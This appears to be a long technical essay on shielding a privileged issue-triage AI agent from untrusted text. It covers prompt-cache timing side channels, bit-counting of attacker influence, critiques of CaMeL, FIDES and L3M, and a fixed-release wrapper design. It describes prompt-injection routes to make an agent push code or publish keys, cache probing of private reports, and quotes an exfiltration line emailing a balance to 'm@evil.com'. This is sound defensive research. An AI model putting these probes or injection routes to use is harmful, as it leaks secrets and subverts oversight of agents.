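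To produce a miss, they sent a new random prompt, which almost certainly matched nothing in the cache. To try for a hit, one account, the "victim", sent a random prompt up to 25 times. A second account, the "attacker", then sent a prompt with the same first 95% and a different ending. They collected 250 response times for each procedure and compared them with a one-sided Kolmogorov–Smirnov test, which an engineer could also use to audit a wrapper. The test finds the largest gap between two curves:

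*D* = max over *t* of [*F*_hit(*t*) − *F*_miss(*t*)]

*F*_hit(*t*) is the share of attempted hits that finished within time *t*, and *F*_miss(*t*) is the same share for misses. If 80% of the attempted hits but 30% of the misses finished within 200 milliseconds, *D*, the largest gap between the two curves, would be at least 0.5. Without caching, both procedures produce misses, so the curves should differ only by chance. The researchers reported caching only if a gap as large as the one they measured had less than a one in 100 million chance of arising without caching.

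The researchers repeated the test with the attacker and victim as the same user, then as two users in one organisation, then as users in different organisations. They detected caching at eight providers, seven of which shared a cache between unrelated customers: Azure, Deep Infra, Fireworks, Lepton, OpenAI, Perplexity and Replicate. At OpenAI and Azure, this affected an embedding model, which turns text into numbers for search. OpenAI's GPT-4o mini and Anthropic's Claude 3 Haiku shared a cache only within an organisation, as the companies' documentation stated.

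A single response time indicated fairly well whether a cache hit had occurred. Average precision was mostly around 0.8, where guessing would score about 0.5. Accuracy was stable for prompts above roughly 1,000 tokens but fell to chance as prompts got shorter. DeepSeek's response times showed no detectable difference between hits and misses, even though its usage record showed that hits had occurred. Hiding the clock from an agent therefore doesn't conceal cache hits if the agent can still read the token counts in the usage record.

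The researchers couldn't recover other people's prompts token by token. They couldn't reliably detect one extra matching token, and each guess they sent could enter the cache and spoil a repeat measurement.

Gu and colleagues reported their findings to the affected providers in October 2024 and gave them at least 60 days before publishing. At least five made changes, such as no longer sharing caches between organisations or updating their documentation. OpenAI fixed its embedding model before the paper came out.

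### Why a cache hit is hard to hide

Separate caches stop customers from learning about each other's prompts, but customers must wait while the model reprocesses text that others have already sent. *Mirage* reports that this isolation raised the median time to first token for ordinary users by roughly 45% on a model with 14 billion parameters. The paper's defence keeps a shared cache and checks for many different guesses after the same sensitive opening. Once the number of guesses exceeds a limit, it delays each reply so that a cache hit looks like a miss, while the hardware processes other requests. In tests with three models, this reduced the success rate of three known attacks to nearly that of guessing.

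Sun and Xiao (2026), in *Where the Savings Go*, found a way to detect a cache hit without timing the reply to the guess. Servers that run language models process waiting requests in steps, each with a limited number of tokens. A hit removes work from the queue, so the requests behind it finish earlier. The attacker sends a burst of requests with the guess in the middle and counts how many steps the others take. In one test, a hit on 1,024 tokens made all 16 requests behind it finish 68 to 69 milliseconds earlier.

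The measure of success was the attacker's *advantage*, which is the probability of answering "cached" when the text is in the cache minus the probability of giving that answer when it is not. With replayed traffic at up to half the server's capacity, one guess about a text of 256 tokens or more gave an advantage of at least 0.98. Delaying only the reply to the guess does not stop this method.

Sun and Xiao didn't test Mirage, but it would probably have the same weakness because it lets the hardware work on other requests at full speed. Mirage also doesn't claim to hide the first few guesses, and this attack needs only one guess.

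Random delays are another option. In Addagada's simulation, noise with a standard deviation of 20 milliseconds cut one attack's success from 100% to under 1%, but a second attack still succeeded every time. Sun and Xiao added the same noise to response times recorded on a real server under load, and their attacker kept an advantage above 0.98. Reducing the attacker's advantage to 0.1 on an idle server required average delays of 0.15 to 4.9 seconds per response, which could easily exceed the time caching saves.

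Addagada's main defence, KVGov, instead adds a secret value for each user, called a salt, to the key that identifies a cache entry, so identical prompts from different users don't match. It stopped all three attacks in simulation, but that result follows from the design, and Addagada didn't test the defence on a real server. A variant adds the salt only where users' prompts begin to differ, so everyone can still reuse the cached shared instructions. Addagada estimates this would keep 93% of the time saved by caching, but hasn't measured it.

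Sun and Xiao also prove that any speed-up a customer can observe from other people's text reveals something about that text, so a cache that leaks nothing can't provide such a speed-up. They recommend a separate salt for each group whose members may safely learn about each other's prompts. Their experiments don't cover any commercial service, and the attack only tests whether a known text is in the cache.

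### Where to put the issue in the prompt

The reader has an advantage over a shared service because its wrapper controls the order of the prompt. Suppose the fixed instructions take 1,200 tokens and an issue with a long log takes 3,000. The reader is one of OpenAI's newer models, which by default puts a cache breakpoint at the end of the latest message, in this case the issue.

| Order of the prompt | Cached tokens, new issue | Cached tokens, same text again | Can the author choose? |
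|---|---|---|---|
| Instructions, then issue | 0 | 4,200 | Yes |
| New random value, then instructions, then issue | 0 | 0 | No |
| Instructions, then the only breakpoint, then issue | 1,200 | 1,200 | No |

In the first layout, the author posts an issue and then posts the same text again within half an hour. They don't need to know the instructions, because the wrapper sends the same ones both times. A hit isn't certain, since OpenAI may send the second request to a machine that doesn't hold the cached entry. Causing a miss is easier, because the author only has to change the first word of the issue.

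In the second layout, the prompts differ from the start, so reposting the issue has no effect on the cache. The wrapper must generate a new value for every call. An issue number isn't enough if a new comment makes the wrapper read the same issue again, because both the number and the text would match. Using a new value each time also prevents the provider from reusing the instructions. OpenAI charges 25% extra to store text in the cache, so the wrapper's operator would pay for unused entries unless they turned caching off.

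The third layout caches the instructions but not the issue, so it still saves on the instructions. The table assumes that an earlier call stored them. OpenAI's guide recommends this arrangement for a model that judges one conversation per call, because paying to store text that won't recur is wasteful. An example deployment reused about 70% of its input tokens. Keeping the untrusted text out of the cache barely slows this kind of reader, since genuine issues rarely repeat one another word for word.

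To get the third layout, the developer has to turn off OpenAI's default placement and set the breakpoint explicitly. With Anthropic's models, the developer should mark the instructions for caching and avoid the automatic mode, which puts the breakpoint at the end of the prompt.

A small signal remains because the cached instructions expire. The call for the first issue after a quiet period uses no cached tokens and the next call uses 1,200, so anyone who files an issue can change the count for the following call. From the count, the agent can learn only that another issue arrived recently, which it can usually see anyway.

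A project that runs its own model may need a different arrangement. vLLM, a widely used program for serving models, stores the prompt in blocks of 16 tokens, so two issues that share only an opening can produce a partial hit. In the first layout, an author who repeated the first 800 tokens of an earlier issue would get 2,000 cached tokens, including the instructions. Repeating more or less of that issue would let the author choose among nearly 190 different counts. This wouldn't work with OpenAI's newer models in the example, because the whole message has to match.

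With vLLM, the developer can put the random value between the instructions and the issue. The 1,200 tokens of instructions fill exactly 75 blocks, which can still be reused, but the issue never matches an earlier one. Addagada gives a similar example with a 2,119-token prompt, where about 124 blocks still match if the difference is at token 1,990, but none match if it is at token 5.

### Testing whether the reader has seen a text

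An outsider might also use the cache to find out whether the reader has recently processed a particular text. This shouldn't work from a separate account at OpenAI or Anthropic, because different organisations don't share a cache. It could work through a reseller that sends many customers' requests from one account, as Sun and Xiao report some do. It could also work on a project's own server if several groups share the server without separate salts.

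An outsider would have to reproduce the wrapper's instructions exactly, but a public workflow file may contain them. If the issue is public, the outsider would learn only that the reader model had processed it recently.

Private vulnerability reports are more sensitive. Suppose one wrapper reads both private reports and public issues, with the same instructions and the first layout. An attacker could guess the text of a private report, post it as a public issue and look for a cache hit, which would be visible if the triage job prints the usage record in a public log. Guessing a whole free-form report is hopeless, but Addagada points out that a form may leave only one field to guess. If the report form had fixed text with a blank for the affected package, the attacker could try one package name per issue.

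The third layout prevents this by keeping the reports out of the cache. A team that wants to cache them can give private reports a separate `prompt_cache_key`, a label that stops OpenAI from reusing cache entries across groups of requests. With Anthropic's API, a separate workspace does the same. The private reader then can't reuse instructions the public reader has stored, but this costs little.

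### From a cache hit to an agent's action

These studies are about secrets leaking from one user to another. None of them tests an isolated reader or demonstrates an attacker steering a privileged agent through a cache. Sun and Xiao also mention attacks that poison or hijack shared caches, but those tamper with stored data instead of using hits as a signal. The way caching works suggests that an attacker could use this signal to influence an agent, but only if the cache covers the issue's text and the agent or its control program notices the difference and reacts in a way that helps the attacker.

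The last condition is the hardest to meet. A cache hit makes a call faster, so it can't cause a timeout, and a miss is normal for a new issue. The time saved is small, about 117 milliseconds in Addagada's longer test, whereas generation time for a reader that reasons first can vary by several seconds. An agent would be more likely to notice the difference with a one-word reader and a very long issue. Hits don't help an attacker use up a rate limit either, because Anthropic doesn't count them towards the limit and OpenAI counts them like any other input.

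Code that reads the token count is a more plausible route. Suppose a developer notices that duplicate issues produce a high `cached_tokens` value and has the agent automatically close any issue with a high value. If a new comment makes the wrapper read an issue again, anyone could comment on a genuine bug report within half an hour and make the agent close it as a duplicate of itself. The wrapper could avoid this problem by comparing the issues' text to find exact duplicates and ignoring matches with the same issue number.

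## Counting the attacker's choices across signals and retries

Each signal that reaches the privileged agent gives an issue's author more results to choose from. A refusal and a timeout each add one, and a cache hit can split one answer into two results that the agent can tell apart. Counting these results lets a team compare two versions of a wrapper, or see how many results a retry adds, before anyone has built an attack.

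### From outcomes to bits

The *outcome set* of a reader call is the set of results that the privileged side can tell apart. If the set has *N* members, the author has at most log₂ *N* *bits of influence* through that call. One bit is a choice between two results, and two bits are a choice among four. Bits are convenient because they add up across calls. For example, two calls with five outcomes each have 25 combined outcomes, and log₂ 25 is twice log₂ 5.

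For most wrappers, the possible outcomes of a call can be counted by adding up the mutually exclusive results, then multiplying by the number of values each accompanying signal can take. A call that ends in yes, no or a refusal has three outcomes, or six if the agent also notices whether the response came quickly or slowly.

The logarithm is an upper limit because the author may be unable to cause every outcome, or to cause it reliably. If *A* is the text of the issue and *O* is the outcome, then

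*I*(*A*; *O*) ≤ *H*(*O*) ≤ log₂ *N*.

*I*(*A*; *O*) measures how much the outcome depends on the text, and *H*(*O*) measures how unpredictable the outcome is. Both equal the logarithm of the number of possible outcomes only if the text determines the outcome and every outcome is equally likely.

### Limits on the answer itself

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, build a version of this idea into FIDES, an agent planner from Microsoft. Like Willison's design, FIDES hides untrusted text in variables and has an isolated model read them. The planner supplies a schema, which constrained decoding enforces on the reply. FIDES orders the possible reply types by how much information they can carry:

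bool ⊑ enum["a", "b", "c"] ⊑ string

A boolean or an enumeration can carry only a bounded amount of information, while a string has no such limit. FIDES adds the reply's type to its security label, next to the marks for trust and secrecy. A policy can then let the agent act on an untrusted boolean but not on an untrusted string. Costa and colleagues justify this by arguing that a boolean limits the influence of untrusted data to one bit.

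That holds for a single value, but the label doesn't track the total across values. When FIDES combines two values, the result takes the higher of their two types, so twenty untrusted booleans together still have the type bool, although they can carry 20 bits. Enumerations also vary widely in capacity. One with the 1,000 values that OpenAI's schemas allow can carry almost 10 bits.

With suitable policies, FIDES stopped every injection attack in AgentDojo, a benchmark for agents that read untrusted data. But Garby and colleagues point out that the evaluation never used the exception for small types, so the result doesn't test the one-bit claim. Costa and colleagues also exclude timing and packet length from their formal model of leaking secrets. So even if a boolean reply limits the answer to one bit, the call's delay may carry more.

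L3M's limit of log₂ 3, or about 1.58, bits per call holds only if timing and failures reveal nothing beyond which of the three words was returned. If an agent can distinguish an "unclear" that arrives after two seconds from one that arrives after a 60-second timeout, the call has four outcomes and the limit rises to 2 bits. Eisenach and colleagues put side channels outside L3M's threat model, so whoever builds the reader has to keep timing and failures from revealing anything more.

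The developer also has to fix the list of permitted answers in advance. Otherwise even a one-bit choice can carry an instruction, as with the pull request whose author chose the file names.

Garby and colleagues show how a program can enforce a fixed list in their agent language. The program makes a trusted copy of the reader's value and releases the copy only if it matches an entry on the list. Any other value keeps its untrusted label, so later checks reject it without stopping the program. They say the attacker's choice carries at most log₂ *n* bits for a list of *n* values, but they leave a formal proof to future work.

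### Counting failures and retries

For the simpler yes-or-no wrapper, the outcome set depends on what a developer lets through.

1. **The agent sees only yes or no.** There are 2 outcomes.
2. **It also sees refusals, parse failures and timeouts, and can tell them apart.** This adds 3, for a total of 5.
3. **The wrapper retries after any failure, up to three attempts.** The agent sees how many attempts the wrapper made and, if all of them failed, how the last one failed. A yes or a no can arrive on any of three attempts, which makes 6 outcomes. The three kinds of final failure bring the total to 9.
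4. **The agent sees the full sequence of attempts.** An answer on the first attempt gives 2 outcomes. One failure followed by an answer gives 3 × 2 = 6, and two failures followed by an answer give 3 × 3 × 2 = 18. Three failures in a row can occur in 3 × 3 × 3 = 27 ways. The total is 2 + 6 + 18 + 27 = 53.

| What the agent sees | Outcomes | Limit for one question | Limit for 20 questions |
|---|---|---|---|
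| Yes or no | 2 | 1 bit | 20 bits |
| L3M's three words, with nothing else visible | 3 | 1.58 bits | 31.7 bits |
| Yes, no or one of three failures | 5 | 2.32 bits | 46.4 bits |
| Attempt count and last failure | 9 | 3.17 bits | 63.4 bits |
| Full sequence of attempts | 53 | 5.73 bits | 114.6 bits |

Small changes to the wrapper can roughly double the count. If the wrapper in step 3 also reports the last failure before a successful answer, the count rises from 9 to 17 (4.09 bits). If the wrapper in step 2 passes on Anthropic's refusal categories, the count rises from 5 to 10 (3.32 bits).

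An attacker's real influence is usually lower than these limits, and the gap is probably largest for retries. The attacker writes one text, and the wrapper resends it unchanged. Text that always causes a refusal will cause three, and the attacker can't arrange a refusal, then a parse failure, then a yes. The attacker can reliably choose only 5 of the 53 sequences: an immediate yes, an immediate no, or three failures of the same kind. Text that makes the reader behave erratically adds some choice, but the attacker can't predict which sequence will follow.

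This protection disappears if the wrapper puts the previous error into the next prompt, a common way to help a model correct itself. A hijacked reader can then distinguish its second attempt from its first, so the issue's author can write separate instructions for each. This brings the author's real influence closer to the full 5.73 bits.

The limits for 20 questions also assume that one person controls every text. If the questions concern 20 issues from 20 people, the limit for one question applies to each author, but on a public repository one person can file all 20. Noise reduces the figures further, since a busy provider causes timeouts that no author planned. Some of the influence is legitimate, because someone who reports a genuine regression should be able to get a yes.

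The count can also be too low because it covers only the listed signals. In the earlier vLLM example, an author could choose among nearly 190 cached-token counts. An agent that could read those counts would receive up to about 7.6 bits per call from them alone, more than from the full sequence of attempts.

### Retry loops outside the count

A wrapper that stops after three attempts has a finite set of outcomes. If another program can restart the wrapper, the set grows with each run, so counting the outcomes of only one run gives too low a total.

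Garby and colleagues found such a loop in CaMeL, Google DeepMind's version of the two-model design. CaMeL's privileged model writes a program, and an interpreter runs it while tracking where each value came from. In their example, an agent manages a customer's account, and an attacker tries to learn the balance with this line:

```python
if account.balance > threshold: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
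```

CaMeL blocks the email because the decision to send it depends on a secret. But the block happens only if the balance is above the threshold. Anyone who can see whether the policy blocked the run learns one bit about the balance.

Most systems of this kind allow a leak of one bit per run. But CaMeL runs its interpreter inside an ordinary Python loop that retries after errors, and nothing tracks information in that loop. A program that controls the loop can rerun the test until it has the whole secret. If the balance is a whole number of dollars below 1,048,576, twenty runs can find it, because each run with a well-chosen threshold halves the remaining range. CaMeL censors the information that passes from one attempt to the next, but Garby and colleagues note that this gives no formal guarantee.

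Their own agent does its retrying in advance, on invented data and with tools that change nothing. If an attempt fails, it revises its program. It then writes a final version to run on the real data. In AgentDojo's banking tasks, using GPT-5.2 and with no attacks, this agent succeeded in 36 of 48 runs, compared with 18 of 48 for CaMeL with its policy checks on. The agent can also relabel untrusted data as trusted, so the figures don't isolate the benefit of retrying in advance. If an error appears only with the real data, the agent can't try again.

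The claim that a failure leaks only one bit is much older than language models. Askarov, Hunt and colleagues, in *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit*, challenged it in 2008. Many tools that checked programs for leaks ignored whether a secret could stop a program from finishing, on the grounds that this revealed at most one bit per run. The paper's counterexample produces output as it runs:

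```
for i = 0 to maxNat
    output i
    if i = secret then loop forever
```

The last number printed is the secret. The tools Jif, FlowCaml and the SPARK Examiner all accepted this kind of program then. An uncaught exception can replace the endless loop, so an observer can exploit the leak without a clock.

Askarov and colleagues also proved that an attacker who watches a single run can do no better than such a brute-force search, which takes impractically long if the secret is long. But a program like this can leak a 32-bit integer in under six seconds, so short secrets have little protection. CaMeL's loop is far more efficient because each run can test a new threshold. It needs twenty runs to find a 20-bit secret, whereas the counting program may have to print a million numbers.

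The arithmetic in both results also applies to an issue's author, even though the results concern leaked secrets and there is no secret for the author to extract. Every rerun adds outcomes, and the total has no limit unless something caps the number of runs. In a triage system, the outer loop might be a nightly job that requeues failed issues, or a workflow that rereads an issue whenever somebody edits it.

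Edits to an issue most closely resemble CaMeL's loop, because the author can change the text between runs. On a public repository, the author can often see how the agent reacted, for example from the label it applied, and adjust the next edit. Twenty edits to one issue then have the same limits as the 20 questions in the table.

Reruns also help an author who wants one particular result. Suppose the author wants a false yes, and the issue makes the reader answer yes 10% of the time, answer no 30% of the time and refuse 60% of the time. If the wrapper retries refusals, up to a total of three attempts, the chance of a false yes rises from 10% to 19.6%, even if the agent sees only the final answer. If the author can instead trigger twenty separate readings through edits, the chance of at least one false yes is about 88%.

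A bit from a refusal isn't useful in the same way as a bit from CaMeL's loop. Whoever controls that loop knows what each blocked run means and can write it down, but the privileged agent has no plan for interpreting a list of refusals.

### What the bits can do

A team could use the count to set a limit. Garby and colleagues mention a *bit budget*, a cap on attacker influence that a policy would track. With a budget of 20 bits, an agent could ask 20 questions if it saw only yes or no, 8 if it also saw the three kinds of failure, and 3 if it saw every attempt. Eisenach and colleagues say that L3M doesn't yet enforce a budget on the messages between its private and public agents.

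Such a budget counts all bits equally, although some are far more dangerous than others. The 114.6 bits in the last row of the table are enough to spell `git push --force` in seven-bit characters. But an agent that sees 20 lists of refusals and timeouts has no reason to read them as letters. The attacker would first have to send it a decoding rule by some other route, and could usually send the command itself that way.

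A 30-character method name, the kind of answer Willison distrusts, holds about 143 bits if it uses only lower-case letters and underscores. This is only about a quarter more than the 20 lists hold, but the agent can read the name directly.

A single bit can be enough to do harm. If the question is whether a pull request is safe to test with the project's credentials, a false yes gives a stranger's code access to those credentials. In branch steering, too, the attacker needs only enough influence to select an existing branch.

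*Attacker Control and Impact for Confidentiality and Integrity* (Askarov and Myers, 2011) gives the example of a service that holds new data under an embargo. The service releases the data if the time stated in a request is at or after the end of the embargo, but the requester writes that time. The timestamp might contain 64 bits, but the service uses it for only one comparison, and a false value releases the data early.

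Their repair adds a check that the stated time isn't in the future. A requester can still choose among billions of past times, but until the embargo ends, all of them return the old data. The check removes the harmful choice and leaves most of the harmless ones, so a count of the possible requests would hardly change.

To describe this difference, Askarov and Myers define *attacker impact* as a set of attacks:

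*p*(*c*[•], *m*, *t*) = { *a* | *c*[*a*], started in memory *m*, produces the trusted events *t* }

Here *c*[•] is a program with gaps that the attacker fills in, *a* is what the attacker puts there, and *m* is the program's starting memory. The trusted events *t* are changes to trusted variables and the program's termination. In a triage system, *a* would be the text of an issue and *t* would be the agent's actions.

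An attacker has more power when the set of issue texts that lead to the same actions is smaller. The author of an issue has no influence if every possible text leads to the same actions, but can steer the agent very precisely if only one text leads to a certain sequence of actions.

The table applies this idea to two handlers for the parser question. Both receive the same five outcomes, so the limit for each is 2.32 bits.

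| What the text makes the reader do | Cautious handler | Unsafe handler |
|---|---|---|
| Answer yes | The agent searches the commit history | The agent searches the commit history |
| Answer no | The agent moves on | The agent moves on |
| Refuse, fail to parse or time out | The agent leaves the issue for a person | The agent opens the issue and reads it |

With the cautious handler, all possible texts fall into three groups by the action they lead to. An author gains nothing by choosing between a refusal and a timeout, because both lead to the same action. The author's influence over the agent's actions is therefore at most log₂ 3 bits, although the agent's side receives five outcomes. With the unsafe handler, the last row splits into a separate group for each instruction that the agent might follow. For example, one text might make it push to the main branch, and another might make it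 publish a key. The bit count doesn't include this influence because it covers only what happens up to the reader call, before the agent opens the issue.

An engineer can work out these groups by reading the code if ordinary code handles the outcomes. If the agent's model decides what to do, the engineer has to run tests, and the groups may change with the next model version. The definition also assumes a deterministic program, in which the same attack always has the same effect. A language model may refuse a text on one run and answer it on the next, so a test can only estimate how often each action follows. The sets don't rank the actions, so somebody still has to decide that publishing a key is worse than spending an afternoon on a useless search.

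Refusals and timeouts raise a further difficulty because they often stop the agent from acting. The basic security condition that Askarov and Myers build on attacker impact requires only that all attacks leading to another trusted event lead to the same one, so a text that merely halts the agent doesn't violate it. Their related measure, *progress impact*, is the set of attacks after which the program still reaches another trusted event. An engineer could use it to check which issues leave a triage agent able to finish the rest of the queue.

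## Building and testing a wrapper that passes only the answer

Even if a handler treats every failure alike, a later change to its code may treat refusals and timeouts differently if the handler can still distinguish them. Merging the failures before they reach the agent is safer. L3M's program for reading web pages already does part of this by turning any failure, timeout or unexpected reply into "unclear". The wrapper below does the same and adds a fixed release time, so that a slow answer looks the same as a quick one.

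### The wrapper step by step

The agent calls `ask` with an issue number and gets back one word.

```python
QUESTION = "Does this issue report a regression in the parser?"
ALLOWED = ("yes", "no", "unclear")

def ask(issue_number):
    start = clock()
    worker = start_process(read_issue, issue_number)
    sleep_until(start + 29)
    answer = worker.result_or_none()
    worker.kill()
    sleep_until(start + 30)
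    return answer if answer in ALLOWED else "unclear"

def read_issue(issue_number):        # runs in the separate process
    text = fetch(issue_number, max_chars=40_000)
    for attempt in (1, 2):
        try:
            reply = run_reader(QUESTION, text, max_tokens=600, timeout=13)
            private_log(issue_number, attempt, reply)
            word = reply.text.strip().lower()
            if reply.finished and word in ALLOWED:
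                return word
        except Exception as error:
            private_log(issue_number, attempt, error)
    return "unclear"
```

1. **Fix the question and the answers first.** Both are constants, so nothing in an issue can reword the question or add a fourth answer.
2. **Limit the reader.** `fetch` raises an error if the issue is longer than 40,000 characters. The reader may write 600 tokens, including reasoning. Even at 50 tokens per second that takes 12 seconds, which leaves one second of the timeout for the fixed delay.
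3. **Retry by a fixed rule.** The second attempt uses the same text and prompt, without the first attempt's error. The wrapper fetches the issue only once, so its author can't change it between attempts. A retry helps with brief service faults, but it also gives a hostile issue a second chance at a false yes.
4. **Check the whole reply.** The reply must be one of the three words, and the reader must have finished normally. Otherwise, a reply that hit the token limit after the first word of "No idea" would count as a no.
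5. **Turn everything else into "unclear".** This covers refusals, parse failures, timeouts, crashes and any stop reason that the provider introduces later.
6. **Discard the rest.** The agent gets no error text, token counts, model name, timestamps or attempt count. In Python, a child process that crashes normally prints its error to the terminal it shares with its parent, so `start_process` has to send that output to the private log.
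7. **Release the answer at a fixed time.** `ask` doesn't wait for the reader to finish. It collects whatever is there after 29 seconds, stops the process, and returns at 30.
8. **Log the details where the agent can't read them.** `private_log` must never raise an error or make the reader wait. If the log is full, it drops the entry silently.

Eisenach and colleagues warn that an isolated reader helps only if the triaging agent doesn't also fetch the page. Releasing the answer at a fixed time would probably require a change to L3M's runtime, because the small programs agents write there can read the clock but can't wait on a timer.

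### Choosing the answer that stands for a failure

When a call fails, returning "unclear" is more truthful than returning "no", and it sends the issue to a person. In the parser example, "no" is a claim about the issue, so the agent would drop a genuine bug report if the provider was busy. Avoiding that is worth a third outcome, even though allowing only two would lower the limit on the author's influence from 1.58 bits to 1 bit per question.

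For other questions, one of the two answers may already mean "stop and ask". If the question is whether a pull request is safe to test with the project's credentials, the wrapper can return "no" for every failure and doesn't need a third answer. L3M handles risky tool calls this way. A second model reviews each call and returns "safe" or "wild", and the runtime counts a missing verdict or an unreachable reviewer as "wild". The proposing agent can then argue its case, and if the two models still disagree, a person decides.

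The wrapper should return the failure value explicitly instead of raising an exception, because other software may control how the exception is handled. *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (Metere, 2026) describes a filter for an agent's outgoing messages. The program that hosts the filter ignores exceptions from its plugins so that a faulty one can't block delivery. A check that raised an exception to stop a message would therefore let it through, so the filter converts exceptions into an explicit "cancel". However, one optional stage, which has a model rephrase each message, sends the original unchanged if the model is unavailable. A wrapper that did the same when its reader failed would pass the raw issue to the agent.

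An "unclear" answer that the reader actually gave must also look the same as a failure in the steps that follow the wrapper. If a triage job labels some issues "reader failed" and others "needs review", an agent that can list labels can tell the two cases apart. Maintainers can find the reason for each result in the private log.

### Fixed and stepped release times

If the reader's median time is 4 seconds, releasing every answer after a fixed 30 seconds adds 26 seconds to a typical question. Processing 250 issues one at a time then takes 2 hours and 5 minutes instead of roughly 17 minutes.

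Running readers in parallel recovers most of that time. With 20 readers at once, the job needs 13 batches of 30 seconds, or six and a half minutes. Each issue still gets its own call, so a refusal affects only one answer. The wrapper should release each batch at its fixed time and in issue order. If it waited for the slowest reader, one hostile issue could delay the other 19 answers, and the agent would see the delay. Parallel calls also reach a rate limit sooner, so the number of readers has to be low enough to keep the call rate well below it.

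Parallel reading doesn't help a developer who is waiting for one answer. A rule with two release times shortens the average wait. The wrapper answers at 5 seconds if the reader has finished by then, and at 30 seconds otherwise. If 80% of calls finish within 5 seconds, the average wait is 10 seconds.

| When the wrapper answers | Average wait | Outcomes | Limit per question |
|---|---|---|---|
| Always after 30 seconds | 30 seconds | 3 | 1.58 bits |
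| After 5 or 30 seconds | 10 seconds | 6 | 2.58 bits |
| After 5 or 30 seconds, but "unclear" only after 30 | Slightly more than 10 seconds | 5 | 2.32 bits |
| At the next multiple of 5 seconds, up to 30 | Less than 10 seconds | 18 | 4.17 bits |

The second release time can leak up to one bit, and an issue's author can control that bit by including a problem that makes the reader reason for longer. Holding every "unclear" until 30 seconds removes one outcome, the early "unclear", so the agent can't tell an immediate refusal from a timeout.

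*Quantitative Mitigation of Timing Side Channels* (2019) treats the choice of release times as an optimisation problem. It starts with groups of running times that an observer can tell apart, and merges groups by delaying the faster ones, within a limit on the added delay. Finding the best fixed way to merge them is NP-hard, so no known algorithm does it efficiently in every case. A wrapper with two release times doesn't need such an algorithm, because a team can try a few values on its own recorded times.

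Rounding send times or adding random delays limits timing leaks less effectively than releasing messages on a fixed schedule. When Metere rounded an agent's message send times, about a fifth of the timing channel remained. Sending messages at a constant rate closed it. Random delays reduced the channel in proportion to their length.

In *The Last Mile*, Cock, Ge and colleagues (2014) studied timing channels on seL4, an operating-system kernel with a mathematical proof of correctness. They calculated that, for a channel that could carry 12 bits, cutting the capacity by more than a factor of ten would take huge amounts of random noise. They also tested holding back replies from a server running the encryption library OpenSSL until a fixed minimum time had passed. This worked better than an earlier fix that tried to make OpenSSL's own code take constant time, which still leaked on ARM processors.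 It also added only 10 microseconds of delay, compared with 60 for the earlier fix.

That result favours putting the delay outside the reader, where it doesn't depend on how the model works. A minimum time alone isn't enough, because a wrapper that waits at least 30 seconds, and longer if the reader is still running, reveals every call that takes more than 30 seconds. The pseudocode therefore stops the reader at 29 seconds.

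### Predictive mitigation

With a fixed release, the developer must choose a safe time in advance. *Predictive black-box mitigation of timing channels* (Askarov, Zhang and Myers, 2010) introduced a method that adjusts the release time. A *mitigator* around the program delays its outputs so that their timing reveals only a bounded amount of information. The developer can choose any bound, but a lower one makes the system slower.

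*Deterministically Deterring Timing Attacks in Deterland* (2015) gives a short account of how the method works.

1. The mitigator predicts when the next output will be ready, using only information that isn't secret.
2. An output that is ready early waits until the predicted time.
3. If an output is late, the prediction has failed. The mitigator starts a new period, called an *epoch*, with a longer prediction.
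4. Information leaks at these changes, so the mitigator can count them and limit the total.

A triage wrapper could start by predicting a wait of 5 seconds and raise the prediction to 10, 20 and finally 30, without ever lowering it. Over 100 questions, the agent would see waiting times that never decrease. There are 176,851 such sequences, so the timing carries at most 17.4 bits. If the wrapper could choose between 5 and 30 seconds for each question, the limit would be 100 bits.

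The time saved may not last, because one issue that runs the reader for more than 20 seconds raises the release time for every later question to 30 seconds, making the wrapper as slow as one with a fixed release. An attacker could trigger this with the first issue of the night. Resetting the prediction every evening restores the speed but gives the attacker another 17.4 bits each night.

In *Predictive Mitigation of Timing Channels for Interactive Systems*, Zhang, Askarov and Myers extended the method to services that answer requests, with separate predictions for different types of request. They tested it on a web page that needed 49 requests. With seven request types, the page took about 30% longer to load, and the timing could reveal at most 850 bits over 100,000 requests. With two types, the loading time almost tripled.

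Their predictions may use any public information, which would be a mistake for an isolated reader. The length of an issue is public and would predict the reading time well, but the issue's author chooses it. A wrapper that waited longer for longer issues would let the author control a signal. The wrapper could safely base its wait on the time of day, or on how long the reader recently took on a test question that no outsider wrote.

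*Deterland* adds that the workload of a general-purpose machine is hard to predict, and that the method also delays harmless variation. Wei, Harris and colleagues find that the method protects general-purpose programs insufficiently and unevenly. They measure the share of secrets still subject to the worst leak, because a low average can hide a few badly exposed cases. In triage, the exposed case would be the rare issue that breaks a prediction, which is the kind a hostile author would write. A wrapper that runs one question under a hard time limit has a much more predictable workload than those programs, but that also means it has little need for a method that adapts, and a fixed release is simpler and easier to test.

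### What AgenticOS adds

*AgenticOS* (Zhao, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) applies similar measures to a whole operating system for agents, to stop a hijacked agent from leaking data through the pattern of its requests. The system would collect outgoing requests and send them in fixed time windows. It would send outputs in fixed-size blocks, filling unused space with random data. For sensitive tasks, outputs would also have to follow a template or use values from a fixed list.

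The time windows are a form of batching and would suit a triage job that reads issues every ten minutes. Padding is less useful for an isolated reader. "Unclear" is longer than "no", but the agent sees the word itself, so it learns nothing more from the length. Padding would help if the answers crossed a network that an outsider could watch.

AgenticOS is a conceptual design without measurements. Zhao and colleagues say that their defenses can't eliminate all covert channels, because an agent can still signal by choosing whether to make a request. They also acknowledge that fixed windows may add latency. The design gives agents one function that returns the exact time and another that returns the remaining resource budget, and anyone building a triage system should consider carefully whether to include them.

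### What still gets through

Releasing each answer at a fixed time makes an accurate clock harmless, as long as the wrapper releases it on time. Removing the clock would be a weaker defence. Every agent in L3M can read a clock, and Cock and colleagues point out that any program can roughly measure time by its own progress.

**Overruns.** A machine that runs out of memory may return the answer at 31 seconds instead of 30. If a very large issue caused the shortage, its author can use the delay as a signal. The size limit in `fetch` helps, as does running the reader and the timer on separate machines. If `ask` itself crashes, the agent's harness will detect the crash, so a small supervising program that never handles the issue's text should return "unclear" at the usual time. The supervising program can also fail.

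If the provider is down for an hour, every issue comes back as "unclear", so the agent can infer that there is an outage. That does little harm, since an issue's author rarely controls an outage. A rule that stops the job after ten failures in a row is riskier, because anyone can trigger it by filing ten issues that the reader refuses. Instead, the wrapper could ask a test question about a fixed, harmless text every few minutes and pause the job if that fails. The test question and the issues need separate rate limits, or an attacker could make the test question fail by flooding the reader with issues.

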